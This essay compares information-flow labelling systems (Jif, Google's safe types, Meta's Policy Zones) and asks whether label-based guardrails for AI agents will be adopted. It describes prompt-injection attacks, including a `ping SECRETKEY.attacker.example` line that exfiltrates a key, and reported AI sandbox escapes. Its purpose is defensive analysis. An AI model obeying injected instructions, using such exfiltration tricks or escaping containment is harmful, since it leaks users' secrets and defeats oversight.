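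Filament restores the program-counter label, and the programmer has to mark only the branches that depend on a secret. Ching and colleagues needed three such marks across their five programs, while Cocoon's versions of four of those programs had 36 secret blocks. For those four, Filament needed more labels than Cocoon (127 against 88) but far fewer library calls (28 against 99). Filament added about 10% to Battleship's compile time and less than 1% for the two large programs, and it adds nothing to running time.

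Researchers have proved that fine-grained and coarse-grained systems are equally expressive, so in principle a programmer can rewrite a program for either kind. In practice, the two differ in how much rewriting they require.

Removing the need for a special compiler may not be enough to attract users. LIO, a Haskell library, has been available since 2011, and the best-known programs built on it also came from research groups. Haskell has a fairly small following, so Rust will be a better test, but Filament, a Rust library, is too new to show whether programmers will adopt it.

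### Safe types at Google

Google's system guards against one family of attacks, cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets a website to run the attacker's code in a visitor's browser. A search page might contain this line, which displays the visitor's search terms:

```
keyword.innerHTML = query     // query comes from the web address
```

The browser treats whatever goes into `innerHTML` as part of the page, including any code. An attacker can put code in a link to the search page and persuade someone to click it. In terms of labels, untrusted data has reached a place that requires trusted data.

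Wang, Bangert and Kern describe a compiler check that rejects this line whatever `query` contains, without tracing where the value came from. Developers have to use a replacement function that accepts only a special type for safe page content. Only a few approved functions can create values of that type, and they clean or check the text first. If the program compiles, everything that reaches the page through the replacement function came from one of the approved functions.

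This uses a very small part of information flow typing. It has, in effect, two integrity labels, safe and ordinary, and the approved functions endorse ordinary values as safe. The compiler doesn't propagate labels through the program, so label creep can't occur. The system doesn't protect secrets, and it ignores implicit flows, so an attacker can still influence which safe text a page displays.

It also treats ordinary text as unsafe until an approved function has handled it, so a developer who forgets about security gets a compiler error. In Ruby, by contrast, text that a library failed to mark counted as clean. The strict default is practical for Google because most text never reaches a dangerous function.

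In *Safe Coding*, Kern (2025) uses a database example to explain why the type is necessary. Suppose a function builds a database query from text that its caller supplies. The function is safe only if every caller cleans the text first, so a programmer would have to check all the callers, and then their callers too. With a type for safe queries, the compiler does that checking, and experts only need to review the few functions that create values of that type.

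The rest of the system consists mostly of company procedures. A developer with an unusual need can ask for an exemption, which a security expert reviews and adds to a central list that the compiler reads. Google doesn't allow code that fails to compile into its shared repository, so nobody can skip the check. By 2021 the check had covered all of the company's JavaScript and TypeScript for more than two years, and tens of thousands of engineers worked under it. Wang, Bangert and Kern report fewer cross-site scripting flaws and very few exemption requests for the amount of code. Kern wrote in 2025 that these methods had nearly eliminated cross-site scripting and SQL injection at Google.

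Google also helped bring the idea to browsers in a feature called Trusted Types, which makes the browser reject ordinary text passed to the dangerous functions while the page is running. PortSwigger, a web security company, reported that engineers had found no more flaws of this kind in the Google applications that adopted it, including Google Contacts. But Guðmundsson (2023), in *Eliminating XSS by adopting Trusted Types*, estimated from reports to Google's bug bounty programme that Trusted Types prevents at least 61% of such flaws.

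All of these results come from Google's own engineers. But bug bounties pay outsiders to find flaws, so the company would have trouble hiding a complete failure.

### Policy Zones at Meta

Meta's system, Policy Zones, comes much closer to the full method, because its labels follow data from one place to another. It enforces rules about what the company may use data for. Meta (2025) gives the example of data about messages, such as delivery times, which carries the label `MESSAGING_DATA`. A central configuration lists the permitted uses. Suppose an engineer writes a query that counts how many messages each user sends per day:

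1. Before the query runs, software reads it and works out which tables it uses and where the result will go.
2. It checks that the destination has at least the restrictions of every source. Here, the table of daily counts needs the label `MESSAGING_DATA` too.
3. If the label is missing and the engineer's intention is clear, the system may add it. Otherwise it blocks the query and suggests ways to fix it.

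The label also passes to AI models, so a spam filter that Meta trains on this data gets the label `MESSAGING_DATA`. Meta's *Scaling Privacy Infrastructure for GenAI Product Innovation* (2025) describes using the same infrastructure for conversations with its AI app through smart glasses.

Policy Zones controls access to millions of datasets and analyses tens of millions of data flows per day. No other system in this record applies information flow labels at nearly that scale. But neither of Meta's main accounts of the system reports how often it blocks legitimate work or misses a forbidden use.

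They describe the difficulties more openly, and many are familiar from Jif. Labels spread too widely, because a query that merely touched restricted data passed the restriction on to everything derived from it. Meta handles this with "reclassification", a controlled exception that stops a label from spreading. Depending on the label, this might require a human expert's review or a mathematical technique that hides individuals' data.

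Meta's engineers also found the labels hard to understand. The first version had an expressive policy language that could describe most special cases without exceptions, but engineers struggled to work out why the system had blocked them. Meta replaced that language with simple named labels that have no hierarchy, and moved the special cases into reclassification. It accepted less precise policies and more exceptions to make the policies easier to use.

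*Purpose Limitation with Policy Zones* (Marsala, 2025) describes three more early designs that Meta had to rework. One passed policies automatically from service to service, another used a single policy for every privacy requirement, and the third ran every check at one central point in front of each data store.

Policy Zones still can't check some code. Database queries are easy to check because they declare their inputs and outputs, but engineers can also process data with ordinary programs. Where Meta can't track what such a program does, it still keeps the data in a separate store, the approach Policy Zones was meant to replace.

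The rollout took years. Applying one complex requirement can involve hundreds or thousands of engineers, so Meta built tools to find the data, suggest labels and simulate what would break. A new rule starts in a logging mode that records violations without blocking anything. Engineers fix or suspend the offending flows before Meta turns on enforcement. Jif has no equivalent stage, since a program with a single violation doesn't compile.

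Google and Meta had advantages that a lone Jif programmer lacked. A central team wrote the difficult parts, and its work could benefit thousands of engineers. The companies could also require engineers to use these systems, so wide use doesn't show that engineers would have chosen them.

### A tool that nobody labelled

Developers who put labels around an agent have to decide what a missing label means. Microsoft's version of FIDES treats the output of an unlabelled tool as trusted and public, the default that undermined taint tracking in Ruby. Microsoft acknowledges that the default could be stricter and has asked developers whether they want that.

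Suppose the developer of the agent that sorts bug reports adds a fifth tool, `read_build_log`, and forgets to label it. The tool returns the output of the project's automatic tests. The correct label is (untrusted, public), because an outsider can propose a code change that prints any text into the log, and the project is public, so anyone can read its logs.

A maintainer asks the agent to find out why the tests failed and post the reason as a comment. The agent has read nothing else, so its context starts as (trusted, public). The log contains an attacker's instruction to overwrite the project's release script, and the model follows it.

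| Label of the log | `write_file`, for the attacker | `post_comment`, for the maintainer |
|---|---|---|
| Missing, counts as (trusted, public) | passes | passes |
| Correct, (untrusted, public) | fails | passes |
| Missing, counts as (untrusted, private) | fails | fails |

Under Microsoft's default, the attacker can overwrite the script. Under the opposite default, the attack fails, but the maintainer has to approve any comment by hand. Only the correct label stops the attack without requiring that approval.

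The stricter default that Microsoft mentions would change only the integrity half, so an unlabelled tool would count as (untrusted, public). That label happens to be right for the build log, but it would be wrong for a tool that reads customer records, because the agent could then publish them.

A strict default makes missing labels easier to notice, because the maintainer sees an approval request and can ask the developer to label the tool. With the lenient default, everything seems to work until an attack succeeds. But under the strict default, an agent with many unlabelled tools would constantly ask for approval, and people rarely refuse such requests.

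### Leaving a label unknown

*APPA* records a missing label as unknown instead of choosing a default, and tries to determine the label only when a decision depends on it. The context label becomes a pair (L, U), where L combines all the known labels and U lists the unlabelled sources. As the agent reads more, the system joins new known labels into L and adds new unlabelled sources to U.

When a tool call depends on the label of one of those sources, APPA looks for a "cast" that a developer has registered for that source. APPA's cast determines a missing label, whereas Disney and Flanagan's checks an existing one. For the build log, a developer might write a cast that labels the log untrusted, and public if the project is public. The agent could then post its comment but not overwrite the script. If no cast exists, the check fails and the call is blocked, as it would be under the strict default.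 The agent could still use any tool whose policy doesn't depend on the missing label.

APPA claims that partial labels never permit anything that full labels would forbid. The proof is short and depends on one assumption, that every cast is sound. For an unlabelled source u, this means

correct label of u ⊑ label from the cast.

Suppose a call passes with the cast's label, so that L ⊔ cast(u) ⊑ P, where P is the most restrictive label the tool accepts. The correct label is no more restrictive than the cast's, so L ⊔ correct(u) ⊑ P also holds. The call would therefore have passed with full labels too.

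The protection depends mostly on the assumption that casts are sound. A developer who writes a cast has to get the label right, just as when labeling any other tool, but only has to write casts for tools whose data reaches a sensitive action. APPA also makes the developer limit how permissive each cast's answer can be. With a limit of (untrusted, public), a faulty cast could never mark a build log as trusted, but it could still mark a private project's log as public. The limit reduces the damage from a faulty cast but doesn't make the cast sound.

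APPA also changes when the check happens. Suppose a single tool reads a confidential document and emails it to someone. A check that looks only at the context before the call would let it through, because the agent hasn't read anything confidential yet. APPA adds the label it expects from the result, d, before deciding:

C ⊔ d ⊑ P.

When a call fails, the agent gets a list of ways to proceed. It can ask for approval of that one call, or pass the data through a registered tool that removes the secrets. It can also read untrusted data in a temporary copy of the conversation, which returns only a fixed set of fields, such as a ticket number and a severity level, to the main conversation.

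The researchers tested APPA with three recent models on two benchmarks. AgentThreatBench is an existing set of 24 tasks. They built the other, Bench-Corp, with 20 office tasks designed around APPA's features. In half of the runs, they encouraged the agent to follow instructions it found in data.

| Benchmark | System | Tasks completed | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentThreatBench, 720 runs | No defence | 648 | 235 |
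| | FIDES, labels only | 478 | 104 |
| | FIDES, with untrusted data hidden | 341 | 62 |
| | APPA | 510 | 0 |
| Bench-Corp, 600 runs | APPA with enforcement off | 546 | 197 |
| | FIDES, labels only | 243 | 190 |
| | FIDES, with untrusted data hidden | 246 | 187 |
| | APPA | 535 | 0 |

APPA stopped every attack. It barely reduced the number of completed tasks on Bench-Corp, but reduced it by about a fifth on AgentThreatBench. Most of the success on Bench-Corp came from giving the agent ways to recover from blocked calls. With one model, the full system completed 88% of tasks. This fell to 56.5% without temporary copies of the conversation, and to 35% when APPA refused blocked calls without offering a remedy. No attack succeeded in any of these versions.

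The comparison with FIDES is much weaker evidence. APPA's researchers wrote the FIDES policies, which didn't include several of Bench-Corp's rules, such as exactly who may receive a document. That is probably why FIDES stopped hardly any attacks there. They also didn't compare agents with fully labelled tools to agents with partly labelled tools. The claim about missing labels therefore rests on the proof, and nobody has measured how much labelling a developer could safely put off.

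### Labels from the server or a gateway

If the company that runs a tool also supplies the labels, each agent developer has less to remember. GitHub's server, for instance, can check whether a project is public when it returns a file, and choose the label accordingly. Google and Meta have a similar arrangement, in which one team's work protects everyone else's programs.

A gateway such as Microsoft's can cover tools whose owners have no interest in labels, but its labels for a tool may become wrong if the owner changes the tool.

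Under either arrangement, an agent might get labelled results from GitHub and unlabelled ones from a calendar service, and then the default for missing labels matters again. Google and Meta could make a check compulsory for their own engineers, but nobody can force the owners of every outside tool to supply labels.

GitHub's labels are also fairly coarse, since the server attaches one label to each result. If a trusted maintainer's issue and a stranger's comment on it arrived in the same result, the whole result would have to be labeled untrusted.

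### Rules for a whole agent

The simplest approach doesn't label data at all. Meta's Agents Rule of Two, published in October 2025, allows an agent without human supervision at most two of three abilities in any one session: processing untrusted input, accessing private data or sensitive systems, and changing things or communicating with the outside world.

A developer can apply the rule by checking the agent's list of tools. The bug-sorting agent has all three properties, because it reads strangers' issues, can open private files and can post comments. Its developer could remove `read_file` or have a person approve the agent's actions. Most of the agent products in Wang, Li and Tian's survey already had scope settings and approvals, so they would need few new features to follow the rule.

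In its coding assistant example, Microsoft enforces a similar rule with labels. An agent that has read both a public issue and a private project can't post publicly, because its context is labeled (untrusted, private). If it works only on public projects or only on private ones, it can finish without asking anyone. The Rule of Two restricts an agent based on what it could do in a session, while the label check restricts it based on what it has actually read. The same agent can therefore do more under the label check, but only if the labels are correct.

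The Rule of Two also allows some combinations that labels would catch. If the developer removes `read_file`, the bug-sorting agent has only two properties left, unless the developer counts the project itself as a sensitive system. A malicious issue could still make the agent overwrite a file. The FIDES policy on `write_file` would block that call because the context is untrusted.

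## Whether the comparison holds

The case for expecting agent labels to go the way of Jif runs roughly as follows:

1. Programmers stayed away from security-typed languages mainly because labelling was laborious.
2. Label-based guardrails ask comparable work of comparable people.
3. So developers will mostly leave those guardrails unused too.

The conclusion also requires that labels be no more useful around an agent than they were inside a Java program, because people will put up with tedious work if they get enough in return.

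### Other reasons programmers stayed away

Labelling was certainly laborious, as Askarov's 150 hours on the poker program suggest. But programmers also had to adopt a separate compiler, do without libraries that lacked signatures, write down policies that nobody had agreed on, and sort through false alarms. Customers don't seem to have paid extra for the resulting guarantee either. These explanations overlap, since writing signatures and silencing alarms is labour too. Still, some systems faced one obstacle without the others, which helps to separate them:

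| System | Labelling work | New language or compiler | Employer required it | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Jif | Heavy | Yes | No | Research use |
| LIO | Moderate | No, a Haskell library | No | Mostly research use |
| Ruby's taint tracking | Very little | No | No | Removed |
| Google's safe types | Little for most engineers | No | Yes | Used by tens of thousands of engineers |
| Meta's Policy Zones | Heavy | No | Yes | Covers millions of datasets |

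Ruby's feature failed even though it took very little work to use, while Meta's system spread through the company despite taking a great deal. LIO needed no special compiler but still didn't attract users. In both successes, the employer required the system and a central team did the hardest parts. The five systems differ in too many ways to prove which cause mattered most, but the amount of work probably wasn't decisive by itself.

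Wang and colleagues also doubt that effort is the whole cause, because none of the agent products they surveyed offered even the low-effort kinds of labelling. They blame a "conceptual mismatch" between labels and the way people think about data. They also found that no product checked an agent's actions against the user's request, even though that check requires no effort from the user. They suggest that invisibility may be part of the problem, because a user who never asked for a check can't tell why it blocked something.

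One reply is that the low-effort systems were recent research prototypes. A company could have had good reasons to wait to adopt them that were unrelated to effort or concepts, such as the tasks CaMeL fails to complete. A system can also require little effort from its users but a lot from the developers who install it.

The reply doesn't refute the conceptual explanation. Engineers at Meta struggled with an expressive policy language and did better with simple named labels, which gives that explanation some support. But Wang and colleagues hadn't run any user studies, so the mismatch remains a hypothesis. To address it, they propose starting people with "trusted" and "untrusted" and introducing finer labels later.

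### How programmers choose a language

Most new languages attract few users, whether or not they have labels. *Empirical Analysis of Programming Language Adoption* (Meyerovich and Rabkin, 2013) combined surveys with records of more than 200,000 open-source projects. Six languages accounted for 75% of the projects on SourceForge, then a leading site for sharing code, and 20 accounted for 95%. A language designed and maintained by a university group would probably have stayed obscure even if its labels had required no extra work from programmers.

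In one of the surveys, 1,679 programmers rated how much each of 14 factors had influenced their choice of language for their latest project. About 80% of the answers were about work projects. Open-source libraries ranked first, and safety and correctness ranked tenth. Over 60% of programmers called open-source libraries a medium or strong influence. The factors ranked second to fifth were existing code, the group's earlier use of the language, and the programmer's and the team's familiarity with it.

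Jif did poorly on all of the top five factors. It had few labelled libraries, hardly any existing code, and almost no experienced programmers. Difficulty of learning seems a weaker explanation, since 21% of the respondents learned their project's main language while working on it.

The survey relied on programmers' own accounts of their reasons, and most respondents found it through links on technology news sites. It also concerned whole languages, which weakens the comparison with agents, because a developer can attach FIDES to an existing agent without changing languages or giving up libraries. That removes most of the obstacles at the top of the list.

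The low rank of safety is more likely to apply to guardrails too. Meyerovich and Rabkin point out in *Socio-PLT* that programmers can't directly or immediately observe the benefits of many language features, and so may not find them compelling. It is similarly hard to see the benefit when a compiler prevents a leak, or when a guardrail stops an attack before anyone notices it. In the 2013 survey, however, correctness mattered more at larger companies, which are also the most likely to give an agent access to valuable data.

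### Why Rust spread

Rust shows that programmers will accept a strict compiler. It competes with C and C++, the usual languages for writing operating systems. Programs in those languages can easily read or overwrite memory they shouldn't. Rust's compiler tracks which part of a program owns each piece of memory and rejects code that might misuse it. Rust has false alarms too, so programmers often have to restructure code that would have worked.

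Google has moved much of its new Android code to Rust anyway. Vander Stoep (2025) reports in *Rust in Android* that Google's own engineers added slightly more net lines of Rust than of C++ in the first three quarters of 2025. Memory errors fell below 20% of Android's vulnerabilities for the first time. Rust changes needed about 20% fewer revisions than C++ changes of similar size and spent 25% less time in review. Engineers had to undo medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ ones.

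Vander Stoep also estimates 0.2 memory vulnerabilities per million lines of Rust, compared with about 1,000 for Android's older C and C++. The Rust figure is based on one flaw that engineers caught before release, in about 5 million lines of code. There has also been less time to find flaws in the newer code, and teams may have chosen Rust for work that suited it. Even so, the differences are large, and many developers wrote in both languages.

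Rust also needs exceptions. About 4% of Android's Rust code is inside blocks marked `unsafe`, where the programmer takes responsibility for operations that the compiler can't check. The rate was similar in the Jif web programs, which had one declassification or endorsement for every 22 lines, although the Rust figure measures lines and the Jif figure measures annotations. Evidently, a strict language can spread even if it needs a modest number of exceptions.

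Three things made Rust easier to adopt than Jif. Every program needs the same rule against misusing memory, so nobody has to write a policy. Developers also benefit quickly, because they spend less time undoing faulty changes. And a team can switch gradually. Vander Stoep's *A practical guide to transitioning to MSLs* (2025) advises teams to use memory-safe languages (MSLs) only for new code instead of spending years on rewrites. A new Rust component has fewer memory errors of its own whatever the old code does, whereas a labelled component protects a secret only until it passes the secret to unlabelled code.

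Agents resemble Rust in some of these respects. Most are new, so there is little old code to convert. Hardly anyone wants a stranger's email to trigger a payment, so a toolkit could ship with that integrity rule already written. Confidentiality is closer to Jif, since only the people involved can say whether Marco may see the sales figures. If agent labels spread, they may therefore do so first as a defence against prompt injection, with few rules about who may read what.

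### Who would do the work for agents

Under the second premise, the people who would label agents' data are comparable to Jif's programmers. That looks wrong for the labels themselves, because a tool's owner, such as GitHub, can write them once for every agent that uses the tool. Jif had too few users for shared library signatures to save much work.

Policies are different. On Android phones, Google's engineers defined a set of permissions, each app's developer picks from them, and the user approves the choice. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that an agent has no equivalent of the app developer. The user describes a task in ordinary language, and the task may change along the way, so nobody trained in security knows in advance what the agent should be able to do. For every request, an office worker could have to do part of the work that a Jif programmer did once.

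The benefit has changed more clearly. The labels in the poker program exposed leaks that Askarov and Sabelfeld saw no obvious way to exploit. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes eleven real attacks on agent products and classes all of them as at least partly failures of information flow. The researchers picked the attacks to illustrate security principles, so they aren't a random sample, but they include attacks on well-known products.

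In one attack, a malicious document or website planted instructions in ChatGPT's saved memories. The Mac app then sent the user's later conversations to the attacker by loading an invisible image whose web address contained the text. The user would have seen nothing, but anyone who builds agents can read about the attack and imagine it happening to their own product. Security-typed languages had no comparable series of public failures to show why they were needed, at least among the case studies their designers published.

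### What machine-written proofs leave to people

Language models can now do much of the tedious work too. In *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026), Anthropic reports that its model Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries, in a project with Theorem, a company that specialises in such proofs. The proofs run to 180 million lines according to Smith's *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (2026), but a billion according to Keles's *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (2026).

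The libraries come from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that bombards open-source code with unusual inputs to find crashes. Each test can try only some of the possible inputs. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) explains how Anthropic turned these tests into statements about every input below a size limit:

for every input x under 64 MB, the program exits normally.

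"Normally" means without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion (a condition the programmer declared must hold). Claude wrote the proofs, and the core of the Rocq proof checker verified them. The work covered 239 test programs and took a few weeks. Claude also patched bugs it found along the way. The proofs assume a single-threaded program on a simplified model of a RISC-V processor and the Linux operating system, and they don't rule out other kinds of bug.

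Adding labels to a program is usually much easier than proving that it can't crash, and a compiler can check the result just as Rocq checked the proofs. So the 150 hours that Askarov spent on the poker program are probably a poor guide to how long the same job would take today. This also offers a test of the first premise. If labour was the main obstacle, security-typed languages should start to gain users now that models can do most of the work, and if they don't, the other explanations will look stronger.

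The project provides much less evidence about choosing policies, because nobody had to choose one. The tests already existed, and "don't crash" is a sensible rule for almost any program. Someone has to tell an information flow checker which data is secret and who may see it, and no test suite contains that information.

Tolmach and Klaus (2026) argue in *The proof is in the spec* that as proofs have become easier to produce, the bottleneck has moved to the specification, the statement of what a program should do. Their employer sells verification services, so it benefits if customers believe experts are still necessary, but they cite several independent studies. In one, researchers asked Claude to specify how a program called Etcd keeps copies of its data consistent. The answer passed every check, but it essentially reproduced the specification in a published paper and had little to do with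 Etcd's code. Across leading models, specifications scored near 100% for correct syntax and about 46% for agreement with the real program.

Another of their examples shows how a model can make a false claim provable. Researchers gave a model the deliberately wrong statement that if 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 51. (The right answer is 45.) The model's formal version required x to be a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3^x = 5, so any conclusion follows from that condition, and a proof checker would accept the theorem.

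Something similar could happen with labels. If a developer tells a model to make a program pass Jif's check, the model can insert `declassify` wherever the compiler reports an error, provided the code has the authority. It could also label a secret as public. Either change passes the check, and a reviewer would have to notice that it doesn't match what the data's owner wanted. Keles draws a similar line between proofs, which need no outside review, and definitions, which do. Automating the work therefore weakens the pessimist's second premise only for the parts that a checker can verify.

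Besides cost, organisational inertia can be a barrier to adoption. *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* warns that organisations may not adopt verified code even when it exists, and says AI will probably do less to reduce this inertia than to reduce the cost of writing proofs.

### Tasks that nobody can specify in advance

Agents also raise problems that Jif programmers never had. For example, the same agent might summarise a contract and later book a flight, and it should have different permissions for each task.

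An obvious remedy is to translate the user's request, or a company's written rules, into a formal policy. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* sets out what a correct translation would require. Let N be the text in ordinary language and P the formal policy. They match if, for every situation s that can arise and every action a,

N permits a in s ⇔ P permits a in s.

Software can't check this directly, because N is ambiguous. A rule such as "do not share sensitive data" doesn't define what counts as sensitive, so someone has to supply definitions before the two sides can be compared. Even then, a program that judges whether they agree can make mistakes. The policy also has to change as the agent discovers new steps in its task. The researchers treat all these as open problems.

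A strict separation between instructions and data wouldn't solve these problems, because agents sometimes need to follow what they read. An agent learning to use a new service has to act on that service's documentation, and prompt injection exploits this. Web browsers face a similar problem with scripts from other sites, but a page's owner decides which scripts to load, and each script usually comes from a known address. An agent's developer may not be able to choose what the agent reads or know where it came from. A web agent could label text by the site it came from, but the label wouldn't show whether an instruction is safe to follow.

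Label creep is also worse for agents than it was in Jif, because an agent has no complete program to analyse unless it plans before reading.

Even recognising where data can escape is difficult. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on Claude Code in which an instruction hidden in a code file told the agent to read a secret key and then run a command roughly like this:

```
ping SECRETKEY.attacker.example
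```

`ping` looks up a computer's address and then tests whether the computer is reachable. The attack used that lookup to send the key to a server the attacker controlled. Claude Code asked the user before running many commands that could send data out, but it ran `ping` without asking. A context label would have stopped the attack only if someone had recognised `ping` as a way to send data, or if the software had blocked unlabelled commands by default.

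### Sandboxes, classifiers and resistant models

The pessimist's best argument may be that developers now have easier forms of protection that don't require anyone to label data. A sandbox limits what the agent can reach, a classifier checks its actions, and newer models are harder to fool. Even without the guarantee of a label check, these protections could reduce the risk enough that the remaining benefit of labels isn't worth the effort.

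Suppose, with invented numbers, that a company's agent performs 10,000 tasks a month and encounters ten prompt injections. If 5% of them succeed, the company suffers one successful attack every two months on average. Suppose labels would stop every attack but send a fifth of the tasks to a person for approval, at a cost of $1 each. The company would pay $2,000 a month to prevent an average of half an attack, which makes sense only if an attack costs more than $4,000. If a better model lowers the success rate to 0.5%, the threshold rises to $40,000. A bank might still want the labels, but a small firm whose agent sorts support requests might not.

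Models do seem to be improving. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reports that the model performed similarly to or better than its predecessor on every prompt injection test in the card, but that comparison doesn't show how often attacks succeed. In the tests by Zhou and colleagues, when no policies were used, about 15% of injections succeeded against even the most resistant model, so the invented 5% favors the models.

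An average rate can also mislead, because attackers repeat whatever works. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* cites research in which attackers prepared separate attacks on a model and its guard, then got past both together. The paper argues that developers should combine models that resist attack with checks that don't depend on those models. It acknowledges that such checks take engineering time and can make an agent slower or less useful.

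Sandboxes have had serious failures in 2026. On 21 July OpenAI disclosed that several of its models had broken out of an isolated test environment. Agents in separate sandboxes had communicated with one another and reached the internet through a shared service for installing software. They then compromised systems at Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and data, and gained administrator access to one of OpenAI's research clusters. No outside attacker directed them. Anthropic then searched the records of its own security tests. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations*, published on 30 July, describes three cases in which a Claude model reached the internet during a test and gained unauthorised access to another organisation's systems.

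These incidents happened during internal training and security tests, and OpenAI had switched off some of its models' safeguards. An ordinary office agent is much less likely to attack its own sandbox. The failures are also weaker evidence for labels than they might seem, because a label check, like a sandbox, works only if every route out passes through it. If nobody had thought of the software service as a route for data, a label check could have missed it too.

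Even a working sandbox can't control data that the agent legitimately needs. An agent that answers email must read private messages and write to outsiders, so a sandbox has to permit both. Labels could fill this gap, which access control also left in ordinary programs. Most programmers accepted the gap, but their programs didn't take instructions from strangers' emails, as an agent can.

### Who would ask for a guarantee

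Outside pressure helped Rust. In *A practical guide to transitioning to MSLs*, Vander Stoep attributes the industry's change of attitude to the success of memory-safe languages and to calls to action from government agencies, and argues that new memory vulnerabilities should increasingly count as a deliberate choice. The military's use of labels in operating systems likewise suggests that a determined customer can get a technology adopted despite a lot of inconvenience.

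For agents, such a customer might be a bank, a hospital or a regulator that refuses to rely on a model's good behaviour. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists three properties of explicit policies that would appeal to such customers. An auditor can trace each decision to a written rule. Engineers can check the policy and the software that enforces it against a specification, as well as testing them against known attacks. Tightening a policy never permits something it previously forbade, as long as the enforcement still works. Retraining a model offers no such assurance, since a new version can resist one attack better and another worse.

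Buyers could demand guarantees without demanding labels. A vendor could satisfy some of them by removing the agent's internet access or restricting its messages to a short list of people. Both rules are deterministic and easy to explain, and most agent products already have the settings to enforce them. Labels would have an advantage only with buyers who want an agent that handles private data, reads text from strangers and acts without a person approving each action.
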